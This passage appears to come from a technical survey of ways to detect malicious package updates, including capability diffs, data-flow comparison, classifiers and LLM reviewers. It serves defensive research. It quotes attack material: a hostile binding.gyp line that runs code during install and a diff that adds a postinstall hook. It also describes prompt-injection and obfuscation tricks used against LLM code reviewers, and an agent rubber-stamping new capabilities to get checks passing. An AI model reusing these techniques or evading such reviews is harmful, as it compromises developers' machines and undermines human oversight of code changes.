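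Chainguard also uses the version number as a guide to how large a change to expect. Under *semantic versioning*, a common convention, a move from 1.0.2 to 1.0.3 should contain only bug fixes, while a move to 2.0.0 can change a great deal. atomdrift's *cleave v1.3* (2026) is similarly meant to show whether a release has changed more than is normal for its project. It scores the rate of change from 0 to 1 for each of six aspects of the files, including behaviours, text strings and function names. A later model will use these scores to rank releases by risk. The announcement demonstrates cleave on the backdoored release of xz-utils, a set of compression tools, but gives no error rates.

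The evidence for malcontent's diff mode is also a handful of demonstrations. In *Detecting the Lottie supply-chain attack with malcontent*, Strömberg, the tool's creator, compares two versions of Lottie Web Player, a JavaScript library, one of them compromised. The file's risk level rises from MEDIUM to CRITICAL. Another demonstration uses the desktop phone application 3CX, in which attackers inserted malicious code into an otherwise harmless library. Both attacks were already known, so the demonstrations show what the output looks like but not how many attacks malcontent would miss. Strömberg doesn't expect any tool to tell reliably whether code is malicious, and he leaves it to the reviewer to know which changes are reasonable for the library.

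Users can limit malcontent's output to modified files whose risk level has risen. This shortens the report, but in effect it compares the old and new versions a second time, by risk level instead of by capability. A file already at CRITICAL, the highest level, can therefore gain any number of capabilities without appearing in the report.

A previous release is a good baseline only if it was clean. Versions 1.26.1 and 1.26.2 of agent-framework both stole credentials, so comparing the second with the first could easily have shown no new capability. Chainguard's more recent documentation specifies a "previous, known-good release". For postmark-mcp, the genuine code in Postmark's repository, which the attacker had copied, could also have served as the baseline. Comparing the package with that code would have shown the extra line in every version from 1.0.16 on, not only in 1.0.16.

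For work on a team's own code, the usual baseline is the *merge base*, the commit at which a branch split off from the main line of development. According to Semgrep's *Remove duplicate findings*, its branch scans start from that commit, or from the last one that had a full scan. Comparing a branch with the latest version of the main line can attribute a capability to the wrong person. If a colleague removes an old upload function from the main line after the split, the branch still contains the function, so the comparison reports a network capability that the branch's author never touched. Users of Google's capslock-git-diff can easily make this comparison by accident, because the tool compares whichever two revisions they name. The example in Google's documentation names `main` and a branch.

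Comparing against the merge base can also miss a new capability. This happens if the branch makes the invoice function call `notify` while a colleague changes `notify` on the main line so that it posts to the internet. Comparing either the branch or the main line with the merge base won't connect the invoice function to the network, because the connection exists only after the merge. Comparing the merged code with the main line just before the merge would catch it.

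The third option is an approved record, which capcheck calls a *lock file*. The `init` command analyses the project and saves its current capabilities in a file that developers commit with the code. Each later check repeats the analysis and compares the result with the file. If the code has gained a capability, the check fails and prints the call path. A developer then either removes the call or runs `capcheck update` and commits the new file, so approvals become part of the project's history. The record stays the same until someone updates it, so capabilities can't accumulate through a series of changes that each look minor compared with the previous one.

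However, a capability can be recorded as approved without anyone having reviewed it. The first lock file approves everything the project can already do. After that, when a check fails because of a new capability, the failure message includes the command for accepting it, and a coding agent told to get the checks passing might simply run that command. A reviewer should therefore treat any change to the lock file as the important part of the diff.

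By default, capcheck passes when a capability is removed, and the old entry remains approved until someone updates the file. Code could then regain the capability without failing the check. The `--strict` option prevents this by making the check fail on removals too.

The check's coverage depends on its settings. According to git-pkgs, most projects will probably ignore the noisier categories and watch five: starting programs, calling C code, executing arbitrary code, unsafe memory operations, and modifying system state. The sample configuration ignores both FILES and NETWORK. A Go version of the invoice change would probably fail a check limited to those five categories, but only because of its shell script, not the secret key, the request or the cache file.

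### A test on npm updates

The most complete published example of this kind of subtraction comes from Froh, Gobbi and Kinder (2023), in *Differential Static Analysis for Detecting Malicious Updates to Open Source Packages*. They used CodeQL, GitHub's code-analysis engine, which converts source code into a database that people can query. The queries can search for a particular function or trace data flow between two points. The researchers wrote about 40 of them (the paper gives both 40 and 41) in six classes:

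| Class | What the queries look for |
|---|---|
| Network | requests to servers, and data that flows into them |
| Process | operating-system commands and new processes |
| File access | operations on system or user files, and the related data flows |
| Obfuscation | code that someone has disguised with known techniques |
| Metadata | new dependencies and suspicious installation scripts |
| Code generation | functions such as `eval` that run text as code |

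The first three classes correspond to capabilities, and the other three mostly cover ways to hide code or bring in more of it. Many legitimate packages match some of these queries, so the tool runs all of them on two consecutive versions and keeps only the new findings.

The tool treats two findings as the same if they have the same alert message and file path, even if their line numbers differ. The message contains the suspicious code, so editing that code produces a new finding. If an update adds another finding whose message already exists in the same file, the tool doesn't try to identify which one is new.

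The tool then scores the update by adding up the severities of the queries that have new matches. The researchers gave each query a severity between 0 and 10, based on their knowledge of malware and on how often the pattern occurs in collections of malicious packages. The tool flags any update that scores 10 or more. One new match of severity 10 is enough, as are matches for three queries with severities of 4, 3 and 3. Each query counts only once per update, so ten new matches for a query with severity 4 add only 4.

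The worked example is conventional-changelog, a package with a few hundred lines of code. In version 1.1.24, its main function loaded some options and passed them to another package. In version 1.2.0, an attacker added a long Base64 string and code to import the function that starts processes, decode the string, and run the result as a shell script whenever anyone called the main function. The start of the string decodes to `rm -rf /tmp/.`, the beginning of a command that deletes files from the temporary folder. The script was meant to start a program that mined cryptocurrency on the victim's computer.

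Subtracting the findings for 1.1.24 leaves five:

1. The file imports the module for starting processes.
2. It starts a process as a shell script.
3. It decodes a Base64 string.
4. The encoded string flows into the command that the process runs.
5. The string passes through the decoding step on its way there.

The last two findings make the report especially useful because they connect the separate facts into a description of what the attacker did. If the old version had already contained the same import, the first finding would not have appeared, but the data flows still would have. The attacker also chose a version number that, under semantic versioning, indicates new features. A tool that used the number to judge how much change to expect might have tolerated more change than it would have for 1.1.25.

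Froh and colleagues first tested nine packages that each had one known malicious version. The tool flagged all nine malicious updates, along with four other updates that the researchers counted as false positives, three in pm-controls and one in ua-parser-js. The test was small, and it was not independent because the malware collections that informed the queries included some of the same malicious versions. The researchers expect this overlap to have little effect because the queries describe general behaviour. Even so, the result is better evidence that the method recognises known kinds of attack than that it would catch a new one.

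Froh and colleagues then ran the tool on 25 popular npm packages. The paper's text reports flags on 89 of 6,361 versions (1.4%), but the rows of the accompanying table add up to 82 of 6,117 (1.3%). The abstract in their university's repository also gives 1.3%. The table includes all 25 packages, so a missing row can't explain the difference, which hardly affects the conclusion.

The variation between packages matters more. The tool never flagged 13 of the 25 packages, but it flagged 36 of the 444 versions (8.1%) of vue, a framework for building web pages. Those 36 make up 44% of all the flags in the table. The related packages react and react-dom account for 46% of the versions but only 14 flags, and without them the overall rate is 2.1%. A team's workload would therefore depend heavily on which packages it uses.

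The researchers assumed, without checking, that the flagged updates were harmless, because these packages have millions of downloads a week and no publicly known malicious update among the versions tested. It is reasonable to assume the updates weren't malicious, but as a result the 1.4% figure counts every flag as an error, including any that correctly identified a new capability.

Froh and colleagues point out that the same method could compare individual commits, but they tested it only on published releases. A release usually combines many commits, so a single commit would have fewer new findings and be less likely to reach the threshold of 10. An attacker could also split an addition across several commits that each stay below the threshold, and comparing each commit only with the previous one would not flag any of them.

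## Separating suspicious additions from routine ones

A list of new capabilities does not show whether the code sends a secret to its intended service or somewhere else, because changing the host name in the invoice code does not change the list. Some detectors therefore trace which data goes where. Others use patterns from past attacks to flag suspicious changes, and the newest use a language model to review the change.

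### Tracing a secret to its destination

Data-flow tracking, which the early GuardDog rules used, follows a value from a source to a sink. In the invoice code, two paths meet at the sink, which is the network request:

```
os.environ["BILLING_API_KEY"] → key → {"Authorization": key} → server.request(...)
"billing.example.com" → HTTPSConnection(...) → server → server.request(...)
```

Together they show that the code sends `BILLING_API_KEY` to `billing.example.com`, which is more useful than reporting only that it "reads the environment" and "uses the network". They also show that this code doesn't save the key to disk, because the invoice text reaches both the request and the cache file, but the key reaches only the request.

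Following the invoice text takes looser tracking, because the program puts `inv.total` inside a new string instead of copying it unchanged. *Taint tracking* marks the source value and everything the program computes from it. The marks can spread too far, so a program that logs only the length of a key could look as if it logged the key itself.

A trace can also stop too early. `subprocess.run` normally passes the whole environment to the program it starts, so `after_invoice.sh` can read the key too. A tracker that follows values only through the Python code would miss the path from the key to the script.

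Even a complete trace ends at a host name, and the code doesn't show whether that host belongs to the company's billing provider. If the earlier version of the code already sent this key to this host, the flow is probably routine. If it didn't, the reviewer at least knows to check whether the host belongs to the provider.

### Comparing flows between versions

*RogueOne* (Sofaer, David and colleagues, 2024) describes a detector for npm updates that subtracts the old version's data flows from the new version's. The detector groups objects by origin into *trust domains* instead of using a catalogue of suspicious functions. All objects from one package belong to one domain, on the reasoning that the same developer controls them.

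In the paper's main example, a program reads a secret from the environment, uses it to log in to a private data store, and publishes some of the results to a public store. An attacker adds one line that publishes the secret itself. The program gains no capability, since it already read the secret and already published data. RogueOne finds the change in four steps:

1. It simulates both versions without running them, using placeholder values so that it can explore all the branches. It records four kinds of event: importing a package, reading a property of an object, setting a property, and calling an outside function.
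2. It turns these events into a graph of objects with two kinds of link. A data-flow link means that one object's value depends on another's. An ownership link means that the code behind one object also controls the other.
3. It assigns trust domains. Each imported package or system module owns the objects that its ownership links lead to. The unknown program that calls the package gets a domain of its own, and so do the constants in the package's code, such as host names.
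4. It lists the pairs of domains with a flow between them and keeps the pairs that occur only in the new version.

A pair counts as having a flow under this rule:

```
A → B   if some object is reachable from A along data-flow links
        and from B along ownership links
```

In the example, the old version has flows in both directions between the environment and the private store, and from the private store to the public store. The added line creates a flow from the environment to the public store. That pairing of source and destination is new, so RogueOne flags the update. If the old version already saved a web library's responses to a file, RogueOne would not flag an update that starts saving the library's error messages to a file.

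A JavaScript version of the invoice change would produce several new pairs, such as environment to network and caller to file system. If a later update only replaced the host name, RogueOne would by default find nothing new, because constants already flowed into the same network module. It can tell the two stores apart in the paper's example only because the program reaches them through different packages. Sofaer and colleagues also tested a "Paranoid" setting, which gives each constant its own trust domain. It should catch the new host name, but it also reacts to a reworded log message.

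Dependencies need separate treatment because much of a package's data goes into them. RogueOne analyses their code where it can and ignores a dependency if data sent to it can't go anywhere new, so adding a package that only does calculations doesn't have to raise a flag. In the attack on event-stream, a package that 4,000 others used, a new maintainer added a dependency containing a disguised malicious file, and nobody noticed for a month. RogueOne flags that update because data flows from the new dependency to the program that called event-stream.

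The researchers tested RogueOne on two sets of updates. The first had 333 updates to 12 packages, of which seven were malicious. RogueOne flagged all seven, along with 17 of the 326 harmless ones (5.2%). The second had one update from each of 341 packages, of which 150 were popular, 150 were chosen at random, and 41 had known attacks. The table shows the results for the second set, including those for MalOSS, an earlier scanner that combines static and behavioural analysis.

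| Detector | Malicious updates flagged (of 41) | Harmless updates flagged (of 300) |
|---|---|---|
| RogueOne | 31 (75.6%) | 14 (4.7%) |
| RogueOne, Paranoid setting | 38 (92.7%) | 120 (40.0%) |
| MalOSS, static and behavioural analysis | 14 (34.1%) | 110 (36.7%) |
| MalOSS, new suspicious functions only | 5 (12.2%) | 8 (2.7%) |

The method in the last row is the closest to a plain subtraction of capabilities, and it missed 36 of the 41 attacks. This is fairly good evidence for tracking data flow, but the comparison depends on which functions MalOSS considers suspicious. MalOSS was also designed for packages that were malicious from the start. Because 32 of the 41 attacks stole data from web pages in the user's browser, the results are much weaker evidence about theft of environment variables or files on a server.

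Ten of the browser attacks were in packages that already had the same kinds of flow, and the default setting missed all ten. (The paper attributes another miss to JavaScript syntax that the simulator couldn't handle, which would make eleven misses, but its results list ten.) The Paranoid setting caught eight of the ten, but it also flagged 40% of harmless updates, which few teams would tolerate.

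Across both sets, the default setting flagged about 5% of harmless updates, most often because they added dependencies that it couldn't fully analyse. It flagged only 0.8% of harmless updates for new use of a system function, such as network or file access, and someone looking for new capabilities would count those flags as correct. According to Sofaer and colleagues, checking a false positive usually took no more than two minutes.

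Simulating every branch can take a very long time. The simulator ran past its one-hour limit on 140 of the 674 updates. Skipping large unchanged files reduced that to five, but it makes the analysis less precise when changed code calls the skipped files.

### Learning from known malware

RogueOne flags any new flow between domains, however ordinary. A *classifier* learns from labelled examples which changes tend to accompany malware. Sejfia and Schäfer (2022), in *Practical Automated Detection of Malicious npm Packages*, built a system called Amalfi around eleven features. Nine describe a version's contents:

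- access to personal data such as passwords
- file access, process creation and network access
- cryptography, data encoding and running text as code
- install hooks (commands that run automatically at installation)
- files that look compressed or binary

Amalfi subtracts the previous version's feature values from the new version's. Its last two features are the time since the previous release and the size of the change in version number.

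The web framework jasmin shows why the subtraction helps. In version 0.0.3, an attacker added code that copied passwords from web forms to an outside server. Many packages handle password fields, read cookies and encode data, but jasmin had done none of these before, and its new version number suggested only a small update.

Sejfia and Schäfer trained three kinds of classifier on 643 malicious versions from npm's archive and 1,147 harmless versions of the same packages. The best was a decision tree, which classifies a version through a series of tests on its features. When a classifier flags a version, a second program tries to rebuild the package from its public source code. Attackers usually leave their code out of the public repository, so a package that matches its source is probably harmless. But few packages provide enough information for a rebuild, and after the first day this check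 removed at most two of the decision tree's false positives per day. The check would not help a team review changes to its own code, because there the suspicious code is in the source.

The researchers ran Amalfi on all 96,287 public versions that appeared on npm between 29 July and 4 August 2021, and retrained it each day on the results. It found 95 malicious versions that nobody had reported, and npm removed them all. Amalfi's decision tree produced 932 false positives on the first day and between 6 and 22 on each of the other six. The first-day figure is probably too high, because the researchers checked only some of the flagged versions and assumed the rest were harmless.

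These results provide little evidence about detecting new capabilities. Of the 95 malicious versions, 30 were the first release of a package, so there was no earlier version to compare them with. All 95 contacted a remote host, but Amalfi's features recorded network access in only 10. Amalfi often classified versions correctly from other evidence, such as an install hook or the time between releases. The median time since the previous release was 7 seconds for malicious versions and about 37 minutes for harmless ones.

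Amalfi also misses many malicious versions. When Sejfia and Schäfer repeatedly trained the decision tree on nine-tenths of their collection and tested it on the rest, it found 43% of them. The best of the three classifiers caught two of the seven malicious updates in Sofaer and colleagues' first set. Only 63 of the 643 malicious training examples were malicious versions of otherwise harmless packages, which may well explain the difference.

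An analyst can also turn known malware into rules by hand. Froh, Gobbi and Kinder's CodeQL queries covered broad kinds of behaviour and relied on subtracting the old version's findings. In *GENIE*, Gobbi and Kinder (2024) used the same engine for much narrower queries that need no earlier version. They collected packages that npm had removed, sorted the 75 malicious ones into 12 groups by behaviour, and wrote one query for each group. Each query took 30 to 45 minutes to write on average. One query tracks data from functions that return the computer's name, the user's name and the home directory to the body of a web request. A harmless program might send one of these details, so the final query requires all three to reach the request.

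The queries found 125 unreported malicious packages among more than 1.8 million, with no false positives. npm replaced 124 of them with a security notice and marked the other, which tracked its users, as deprecated. Four of the twelve queries found all 125, and one of those four found 91.

The absence of false positives shows how specific the queries are, but not how much malware they missed. Gobbi and Kinder say that they gave up recall for precision, and that the method can't detect a completely new attack because it needs a known example to copy. Obfuscated code can also break CodeQL's tracking, so they wrote more queries to detect a popular obfuscation tool, although some companies use the same tool to protect paid products.

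The need for a known example is a serious limitation when reviewing a coding agent's work. If an agent adds code that uploads invoices without being asked, that code won't necessarily resemble known data-stealing code.

### Language models as reviewers

A language model can judge a change without a catalogue, hand-written queries or a fixed set of features. *Evaluating LLM-Based Detection of Malicious Package Updates in npm* (Wyss, Tassio and colleagues, 2025) tested this with GPT-4-Turbo, GPT-4o and Gemini 2.0 Flash, all now several generations old.

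Size was the first obstacle. The average package in their collection had about 546,000 tokens (the word fragments that a model reads), and even an ordinary diff had about 116,000. To produce a shorter "smart diff", the researchers' program strips comments from both versions and standardises variable names and layout. It then uses a plagiarism detector to remove code that occurs in both versions of a file, and lists the remaining differences. Smart diffs averaged about 25,000 tokens, but about 1.5% still exceeded the 128,000-token limit of the GPT-4 models. Those have to be split into chunks, which may lack context that the model needs.

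The model received the smart diff and instructions to act as a program analyst, look for malicious behaviour and say whether the update was malicious. The prompt didn't include the update's intended purpose. A small, separate classifier then converted the model's written answer into a verdict.

The researchers used 46 known malicious updates, 163 malicious copies of real packages, and 2,000 typical updates they assumed were harmless. They also ran RogueOne on two of the three sets.

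| Detector | Malicious updates flagged (of 46) | Malicious copies flagged (of 163) | Typical updates flagged (of 2,000) |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 46 | 163 | 8 |
| GPT-4-Turbo | 46 | 163 | 16 |
| Gemini 2.0 Flash | 46 | 163 | 75 |
| RogueOne | 39 | not tested | 124, plus 160 errors |

With GPT-4o, the whole process took a median of 12 seconds per update. At the time, GPT-4-Turbo cost an average of $0.25 per smart diff, compared with $1.16 for an ordinary diff and $5.46 for a whole package. GPT-4o cost half as much per token.

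The perfect recall is less impressive than it looks, mainly because the 163 copies appear to come from a single campaign with similar cryptocurrency-mining scripts, so they amount to far fewer than 163 independent tests. All 46 malicious updates and 54 of the copies were also used to train the classifier that interprets the answers, but this overlap may not matter much because the classifier was trained to read verdicts rather than code.

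The attacks, or articles about them, may also have been in the models' training data. *MalTotal* (2026) raises this concern about language-model detectors and tests its own system on 260 malicious packages from after January 2025, too recent to be in the training data of the two models it checked. The system still performed well, which is some reassurance but doesn't show that Wyss and colleagues' system would have too.

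*How Effective Are NPM Malicious Package Detectors?* (2026) criticises several earlier evaluations, including this one, for reporting overall scores without explaining what produces them. The criticism is a little harsh, since Wyss and colleagues sorted the false positives by cause. Most of these involved sensitive operations, such as starting processes or fetching outside scripts. All three models also flagged an update that only replaced a package's code with a notice that the package was no longer in use. Wyss and colleagues explained the correct flags less fully. On heavily disguised code, the models often cited the disguise itself as a warning sign but had only a superficial understanding of what the code did.

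The researchers also had GPT-4o read 7,661 updates to popular packages as they appeared over nearly three months. It flagged seven, and none turned out to be clearly malicious. One of them, an update to the cdk-assets package, included a test script that uploads a local file to Amazon's storage service. The researchers counted this as a false positive, but the flag would probably have been useful to a reviewer looking for new network and file access.

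Datadog has applied the same idea to *pull requests*, the changes developers submit for review. In *Detecting malicious pull requests at scale with LLMs*, Lamb, Hamsen and colleagues describe BewAIre, a system that gives a language model each diff along with information about its author and repository. It splits large diffs into chunks, between files where possible, and flags the whole change if the model judges any chunk malicious. Datadog had nearly 10,000 pull requests a week at the time. Lamb and colleagues report that six months of tuning reduced the false-positive rate from over 10% to under 0.03%.

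A later test makes the 0.03% figure hard to generalise. In *From single pull requests to full software packages*, Doutre, Peronnet and colleagues report that a single reading by a model produced 17 false positives on 690 test diffs, a rate of at least 2.5%. The later test set may have been harder, and Datadog had also deliberately made the first reading flag changes more readily, because flagged changes now go to a second stage. In that stage, a stronger model can open other files, list commits and check the contributor's history. The second stage eliminated all 17 false positives. The reported accuracy of 99.86% leaves one error among the 690 diffs. Since no false positives remained, that error must be a malicious change that the system missed.

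On full packages, the two-stage system detected 95.5% of confirmed malware, at an estimated cost of about 2.5 cents for a median-sized package. These are a vendor's own figures, measured on data it collected and apparently also used for tuning.

Giving the model access to other files matters because a diff may not contain the decisive evidence. *From Verdict to Diagnosis* (2026) makes this point about pull requests that introduce vulnerabilities. The `notify` helper in the previous section posed the same problem, because its network request was in a file that the change didn't touch. The paper also argues that it is not enough to check whether a reviewer rejects a bad change. Its benchmark has 89 malicious and 50 harmless pull requests, and specifies the vulnerability the reviewer should identify in each malicious one and the code that proves it. Without such a requirement, a model that rejected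 the invoice change because of the time-zone correction would be scored as correct.

### Misleading text in the code

Comments can change a model's assessment of code even though they don't affect what the code does. *ALIBI* (2026) found that language-model vulnerability detectors tend to treat comments as accurate, and that misleading comments can stop them from reporting real vulnerabilities. The experiments covered vulnerabilities rather than new capabilities, but a comment like "required by the billing provider" above an upload could plausibly have the same effect.

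Smart diffs remove this risk by deleting all comments, including honest explanations. Standardising variable names prevents an attacker from making a password look harmless by calling it `retry_count`. But the program can't delete text that the code uses, such as host names and messages. When Wyss and colleagues inserted a passage telling the model to ignore its instructions and report a benign update, all three models flagged it as malicious.

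Mild disguises worked better. The researchers scattered an attack through a large update, passed a network function through a long chain of variables, and assembled the address `pastebin.com` from fragments of one or two characters. Each disguise alone fooled GPT-4-Turbo and Gemini, but GPT-4o missed the attack only when scattering was combined with the other two. Newer models may do better, but the second and third disguises don't require a language model to detect, since ordinary data-flow tracking can follow a chain of assignments and join constant strings. RogueOne tended to miss attacks with complex disguises and branching loops, which the models caught, so there is good reason to use both methods.

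A false description can also count against a change if the model compares it with the code. In 2025, an attacker altered tj-actions/changed-files, a widely used tool for automated builds, so that it printed secrets to build logs. BewAIre flagged the change and listed the misleading commit message among the warning signs. Checking whether a message describes the code accurately is easier than judging whether the code stayed within its task, but both require the model to treat the text as a claim that could be false.

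Host names are harder to check this way, because the code may contain nothing that contradicts them. Doutre and colleagues found that BewAIre's first stage accepted domains that merely resembled Datadog's own. They fixed this with a simple program rather than a better model. The program extracts every domain from the change and compares each one with a fixed list of likely imitations, which Datadog could generate because it knows which domains it owns.

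## Install scripts and other code that runs automatically

Some code in a package runs as soon as a developer installs, builds or imports the package, whereas code in a function runs only when something calls the function. An attacker who adds code that runs automatically can steal credentials from people who never use the package's features, so a detector should report both where a new capability is and when its code would run.

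### What runs, and when

Every npm package contains a `package.json`, which lists its name, version, dependencies and scripts. Scripts named `preinstall`, `install` and `postinstall` are install hooks, which are shell commands that npm runs in that order. According to NodeSource, a company that supports Node.js users, these commands have the same privileges as the developer or automated build that starts the installation. Most of them only compile a module or download a binary.

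npm can also start a build without a hook. Packages that include C or C++ code describe how to compile it in a file called `binding.gyp`. If this file is in the package's top folder and the package has no `preinstall` or `install` script of its own, the default install command is `node-gyp rebuild`, which reads the file and runs the build. Deleting an `install` script from such a package can therefore start a build that did not run before.

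Python packages come as wheels or source distributions. A wheel is already built, so pip, Python's standard installer, only copies its files into place. pip has to build a source distribution first by running the package's build code, often `setup.py`, an ordinary Python program that can open connections, read files or start other programs. A wheel can still contain code that runs automatically later. For example, every time Python starts, it executes any line that begins with `import` in a `.pth` file in its package folder.

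Importing a package runs code in both languages, because the program executes every statement outside a function when it loads the file:

```python
import os

token = os.getenv("API_TOKEN")       # runs on import

def get_token():
    return os.getenv("API_TOKEN")    # runs only when called
```

Both calls read the same variable, and a catalogue of sensitive functions gives them the same label, but the first call runs in every program that imports the file. A function-level comparison has to treat the file's top-level code as a separate unit, or it can't report a call that moves from `get_token` to the top of the file.

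### Comparing install hooks

The simplest check reads `package.json` in both versions and reports any new or changed install hook. It requires no code analysis and would catch a lot of known malware. *On the feasibility of detecting injections in malicious npm packages* (Scalco, Vu and colleagues, 2022) found that 92 of 119 malicious packages (77%) used `package.json` to launch a malicious script at installation. Socket has put the share at 94%. Both figures estimate recall, and neither shows how often the check would flag a harmless package.

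The hook itself reveals little about what the code does, as the attack on jscrambler demonstrates. This package is the command-line tool for a commercial service that disguises JavaScript code to protect it. On 11 July 2026, an attacker published a malicious version, 8.14.0. Prabhu (2026), in *jscrambler npm package publishes malicious preinstall binary*, compared it with 8.13.0, the last clean release. The package had grown from 37.8 kB to 7.9 MB, and `package.json` had a new `preinstall` hook. The hook led to the malware in three steps:

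1. The hook ran `dist/setup.js`, a short, readable script.
2. The script opened `dist/intro.js`, which wasn't JavaScript despite its name. It was a container holding three compressed programs, one each for Linux, Windows and macOS.
3. The script unpacked the right program into the temporary folder under a random name and started it separately from npm, so that it kept running after the installation ended.

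The hook check would flag this update, but only for running a new command. Analysing `setup.js` would also reveal file access and process execution. The code that steals browser passwords and cryptocurrency wallets is in the compiled programs, so an analysis of the JavaScript would miss it. A detector that silently skips files it can't parse would also leave `intro.js` out of its report. But a reviewer who learns that the update unpacks and starts a program that wasn't in the previous version has enough reason to reject it.

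The called file also matters when the hook stays the same. If a package has run `node setup.js` after installation for years and an update adds an upload to `setup.js`, `package.json` stays identical and the check finds nothing. A detector therefore has to follow each hook to the file it runs, and to any files loaded from there, and compare the capabilities of all this code between versions. It also has to analyse the command itself, because in 12 of Scalco and colleagues' 119 packages, the attackers put malicious shell commands directly in `package.json`, mostly to delete folders.

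### A hook in a new dependency

axios is a JavaScript library for making web requests. Help Net Security's *Axios npm packages backdoored in supply chain attack* (2026) cites an estimate of about 100 million downloads a week. On 31 March 2026, an attacker who had taken over a maintainer's account published two malicious versions. Datadog Security Labs' *Compromised axios npm package delivers cross-platform RAT* (2026) found that the source code of one of them, 1.14.1, was identical to that of 1.14.0. The attack depended on two added lines, and only the first was in axios:

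```diff
# axios: package.json, list of dependencies
+    "plain-crypto-js": "^4.2.1"

# plain-crypto-js: package.json, compared with the real crypto-js
+    "postinstall": "node setup.js"
```

plain-crypto-js was a copy of the encryption library crypto-js with a hook added. Anyone who installed the new axios also installed plain-crypto-js, and npm then ran the hook, which downloaded and started a program for controlling the machine remotely. axios had no new hook of its own, so comparing its scripts would have found nothing.

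To catch this, a detector has to repeat the hook check for every package an update brings in, including transitive dependencies. If the project didn't use the package before, everything in it counts as new. Endor Labs, a software security company, also found that none of the 86 files in axios imports plain-crypto-js, which is another warning sign. Some harmless dependencies aren't imported either, such as packages that contain only type definitions, but those don't need to run an install script.

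The attacker also made the hook hard to examine. `setup.js` stored its text in encoded form, including the names of the system modules it loaded, so a search for those names would not have matched. After starting the download, the script deleted itself and replaced its `package.json` with a copy that had no hook, so anyone who inspected the installed folder afterwards would have found nothing wrong. A detector should therefore read the registry's archive before npm installs it.

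### Attacks without a hook

In June 2026, an attacker used `binding.gyp` to run code during installation without declaring any hook. Likhith (2026), in *Miasma npm Supply Chain Attack*, named the technique "Phantom Gyp" and counted 57 affected packages with more than 286 malicious versions. ReversingLabs, another security company, confirmed 56 packages and 286 versions. The attacker added a 157-byte `binding.gyp` to each package, and one line in it started the malware:

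```json
"sources": ["<!(node index.js > /dev/null 2>&1 && echo stub.c)"]
```

The `sources` entry normally lists the C or C++ files to compile. In this format, `<!(...)` runs a command and uses its output as the value. Here the command runs `index.js`, hides its output, and then prints the name of a C file that doesn't exist, which keeps the build from reporting an error. `index.js` decrypts and starts a program that steals credentials and uses them to publish infected versions of other packages.

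Checking for a new `binding.gyp` is as easy as checking for a new hook, and it should cause few false alarms. According to ReversingLabs, well under 1% of npm packages contain the file, and none of the affected packages had any C or C++ code to compile. In packages that do need the file, a detector has to examine the commands inside it. Legitimate build files also use `<!(`, for example to get another package's path from Node.js, so its presence alone isn't enough to flag a file.

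The malicious code in node-ipc, a package for communication between programs, ran without a hook or a build file. Snyk (2026) lists three malicious versions from 14 May 2026. In each, the attacker had added code to `node-ipc.cjs`, one of the package's ordinary files. The Hacker News reports that the code was at the end of the file, outside any function a user would call, and ran whenever a program loaded the package with `require`. It searched for 90 categories of credentials. One of the three versions did nothing unless the program's main file was at a particular path, so a test run with the main file elsewhere would have looked harmless.

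Only a comparison of the package's full code would find this change. Because the attacker had disguised the code, a static detector might not be able to list its capabilities. It could still report that the new version, unlike the old one, runs unreadable code on import, which is unusual enough to justify a closer look.

The jscrambler attacker used both methods on the same afternoon. Versions 8.14.0, 8.16.0 and 8.17.0 ran the loader from an install hook. Version 8.18.0, published five minutes after 8.17.0, had no hook and ran the same loader from the top of `dist/index.js`. SafeDep's *Official jscrambler npm Package Compromised Across Multiple Releases* points out that a scanner looking only for suspicious install scripts would find nothing in that version. Socket's *jscrambler npm Package Compromised in Supply Chain Attack* adds that npm's `--ignore-scripts` option, which turns hooks off,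 doesn't stop the loader in that version.

As with agent-framework, the previous release is a poor baseline here. Version 8.18.0 lacks an install hook that 8.17.0 had, which looks like an improvement. The 7.8 MB container is identical in both versions, so it wouldn't count as new. Comparing 8.18.0 with 8.13.0 would reveal both the container and the loader.

### Comparing a package with its source

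npm installs the archive that the publisher uploaded, which can differ from the public source repository that developers often read to vet a dependency. A developer who reviewed every commit to jscrambler, for example, would have missed the attack on it. The Hacker News (2026) reports that the repository had no commit, tag or pull request matching version 8.14.0. The company's own account, *Security Incident Postmortem* (Fortuna, 2026), confirms that the attacker used a stolen npm token and left the source code unchanged.

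LastPyMile, which Vu and colleagues published in 2021, finds such differences in Python packages. Scalco and colleagues adapted it to npm. Their tool works in four steps:

1. It looks up the address of the source repository in the package's registry entry.
2. It records every line, and a hash (a short fingerprint) of every file, from all the commits in the repository's history.
3. It does the same for the published archive.
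4. It reports "phantom" files and lines, which are in the archive but have never been in the repository.

Searching the whole history means that the tool doesn't need to know which commit a release came from. The output is a smaller body of code in which to look for capabilities. To measure the benefit, the researchers took 37 text patterns from Microsoft's OSS Detect Backdoor scanner and applied them first to whole packages and then only to the phantom code. Adding up their results for individual packages gives these totals:

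| Packages tested | Alerts from the whole package | Alerts from phantom code only |
|---|---|---|
| 10 malicious | 315, of which 282 were false | 39, of which 6 were false |
| 10 popular and harmless | 144, all false | 0 |

Both searches produced the same 33 correct alerts, so the comparison removed almost all the false alerts without reducing recall. Scalco and colleagues report that the share of alerts that were false fell from 90.2% to 21.3%, averaged across the ten malicious packages. Pooling the alerts gives 90% and 15%. In both searches, the patterns missed the malicious code in one package, kraken-api. The comparison did isolate the added file, though, so a person reading the list of phantom files would have had a good chance of spotting it.

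The method was tested on only twenty packages, and it has trouble with generated code. Many projects publish build output that they don't keep in the repository, so every generated line is a phantom, whether or not the release is malicious. jscrambler's `dist` folder contains build output, so the tool might list most of the folder for any version. Excluding files that were also phantoms in the previous clean release would help, since the remaining files for 8.14.0 would include `setup.js` and `intro.js`.

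Another weakness is that the comparison relies on the repository address listed in the registry. Scalco and colleagues assume this address is safe, but whoever publishes the package supplies it, so an attacker could give the address of a copied repository that already contains the malicious code. Using the address from an earlier release would prevent this. The comparison still doesn't help if the attacker changes the real repository, and the jscrambler attacker had write access to jscrambler's repository.

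For axios 1.14.1, the comparison would have shown very little, because the attacker added only the name of a dependency. But there were other signs that the release hadn't gone through the project's normal process. SafeDep's *axios Compromised* (2026) notes that the repository had no tag for 1.14.1. Willison (2026), in *Supply Chain Attack on Axios Pulls Malicious Dependency from npm*, considers a package version with no matching GitHub release a useful warning sign. The publisher had also changed from GitHub's build system for 1.14.0 to a personal account for 1.14.1. The earlier version had used *trusted publishing*, which relies on short-lived credentials instead of a stored token. Nesbitt (2026), in *npm's defaults are bad*, complains that anyone who controls a maintainer's account can switch off trusted publishing without npm alerting the package's users.

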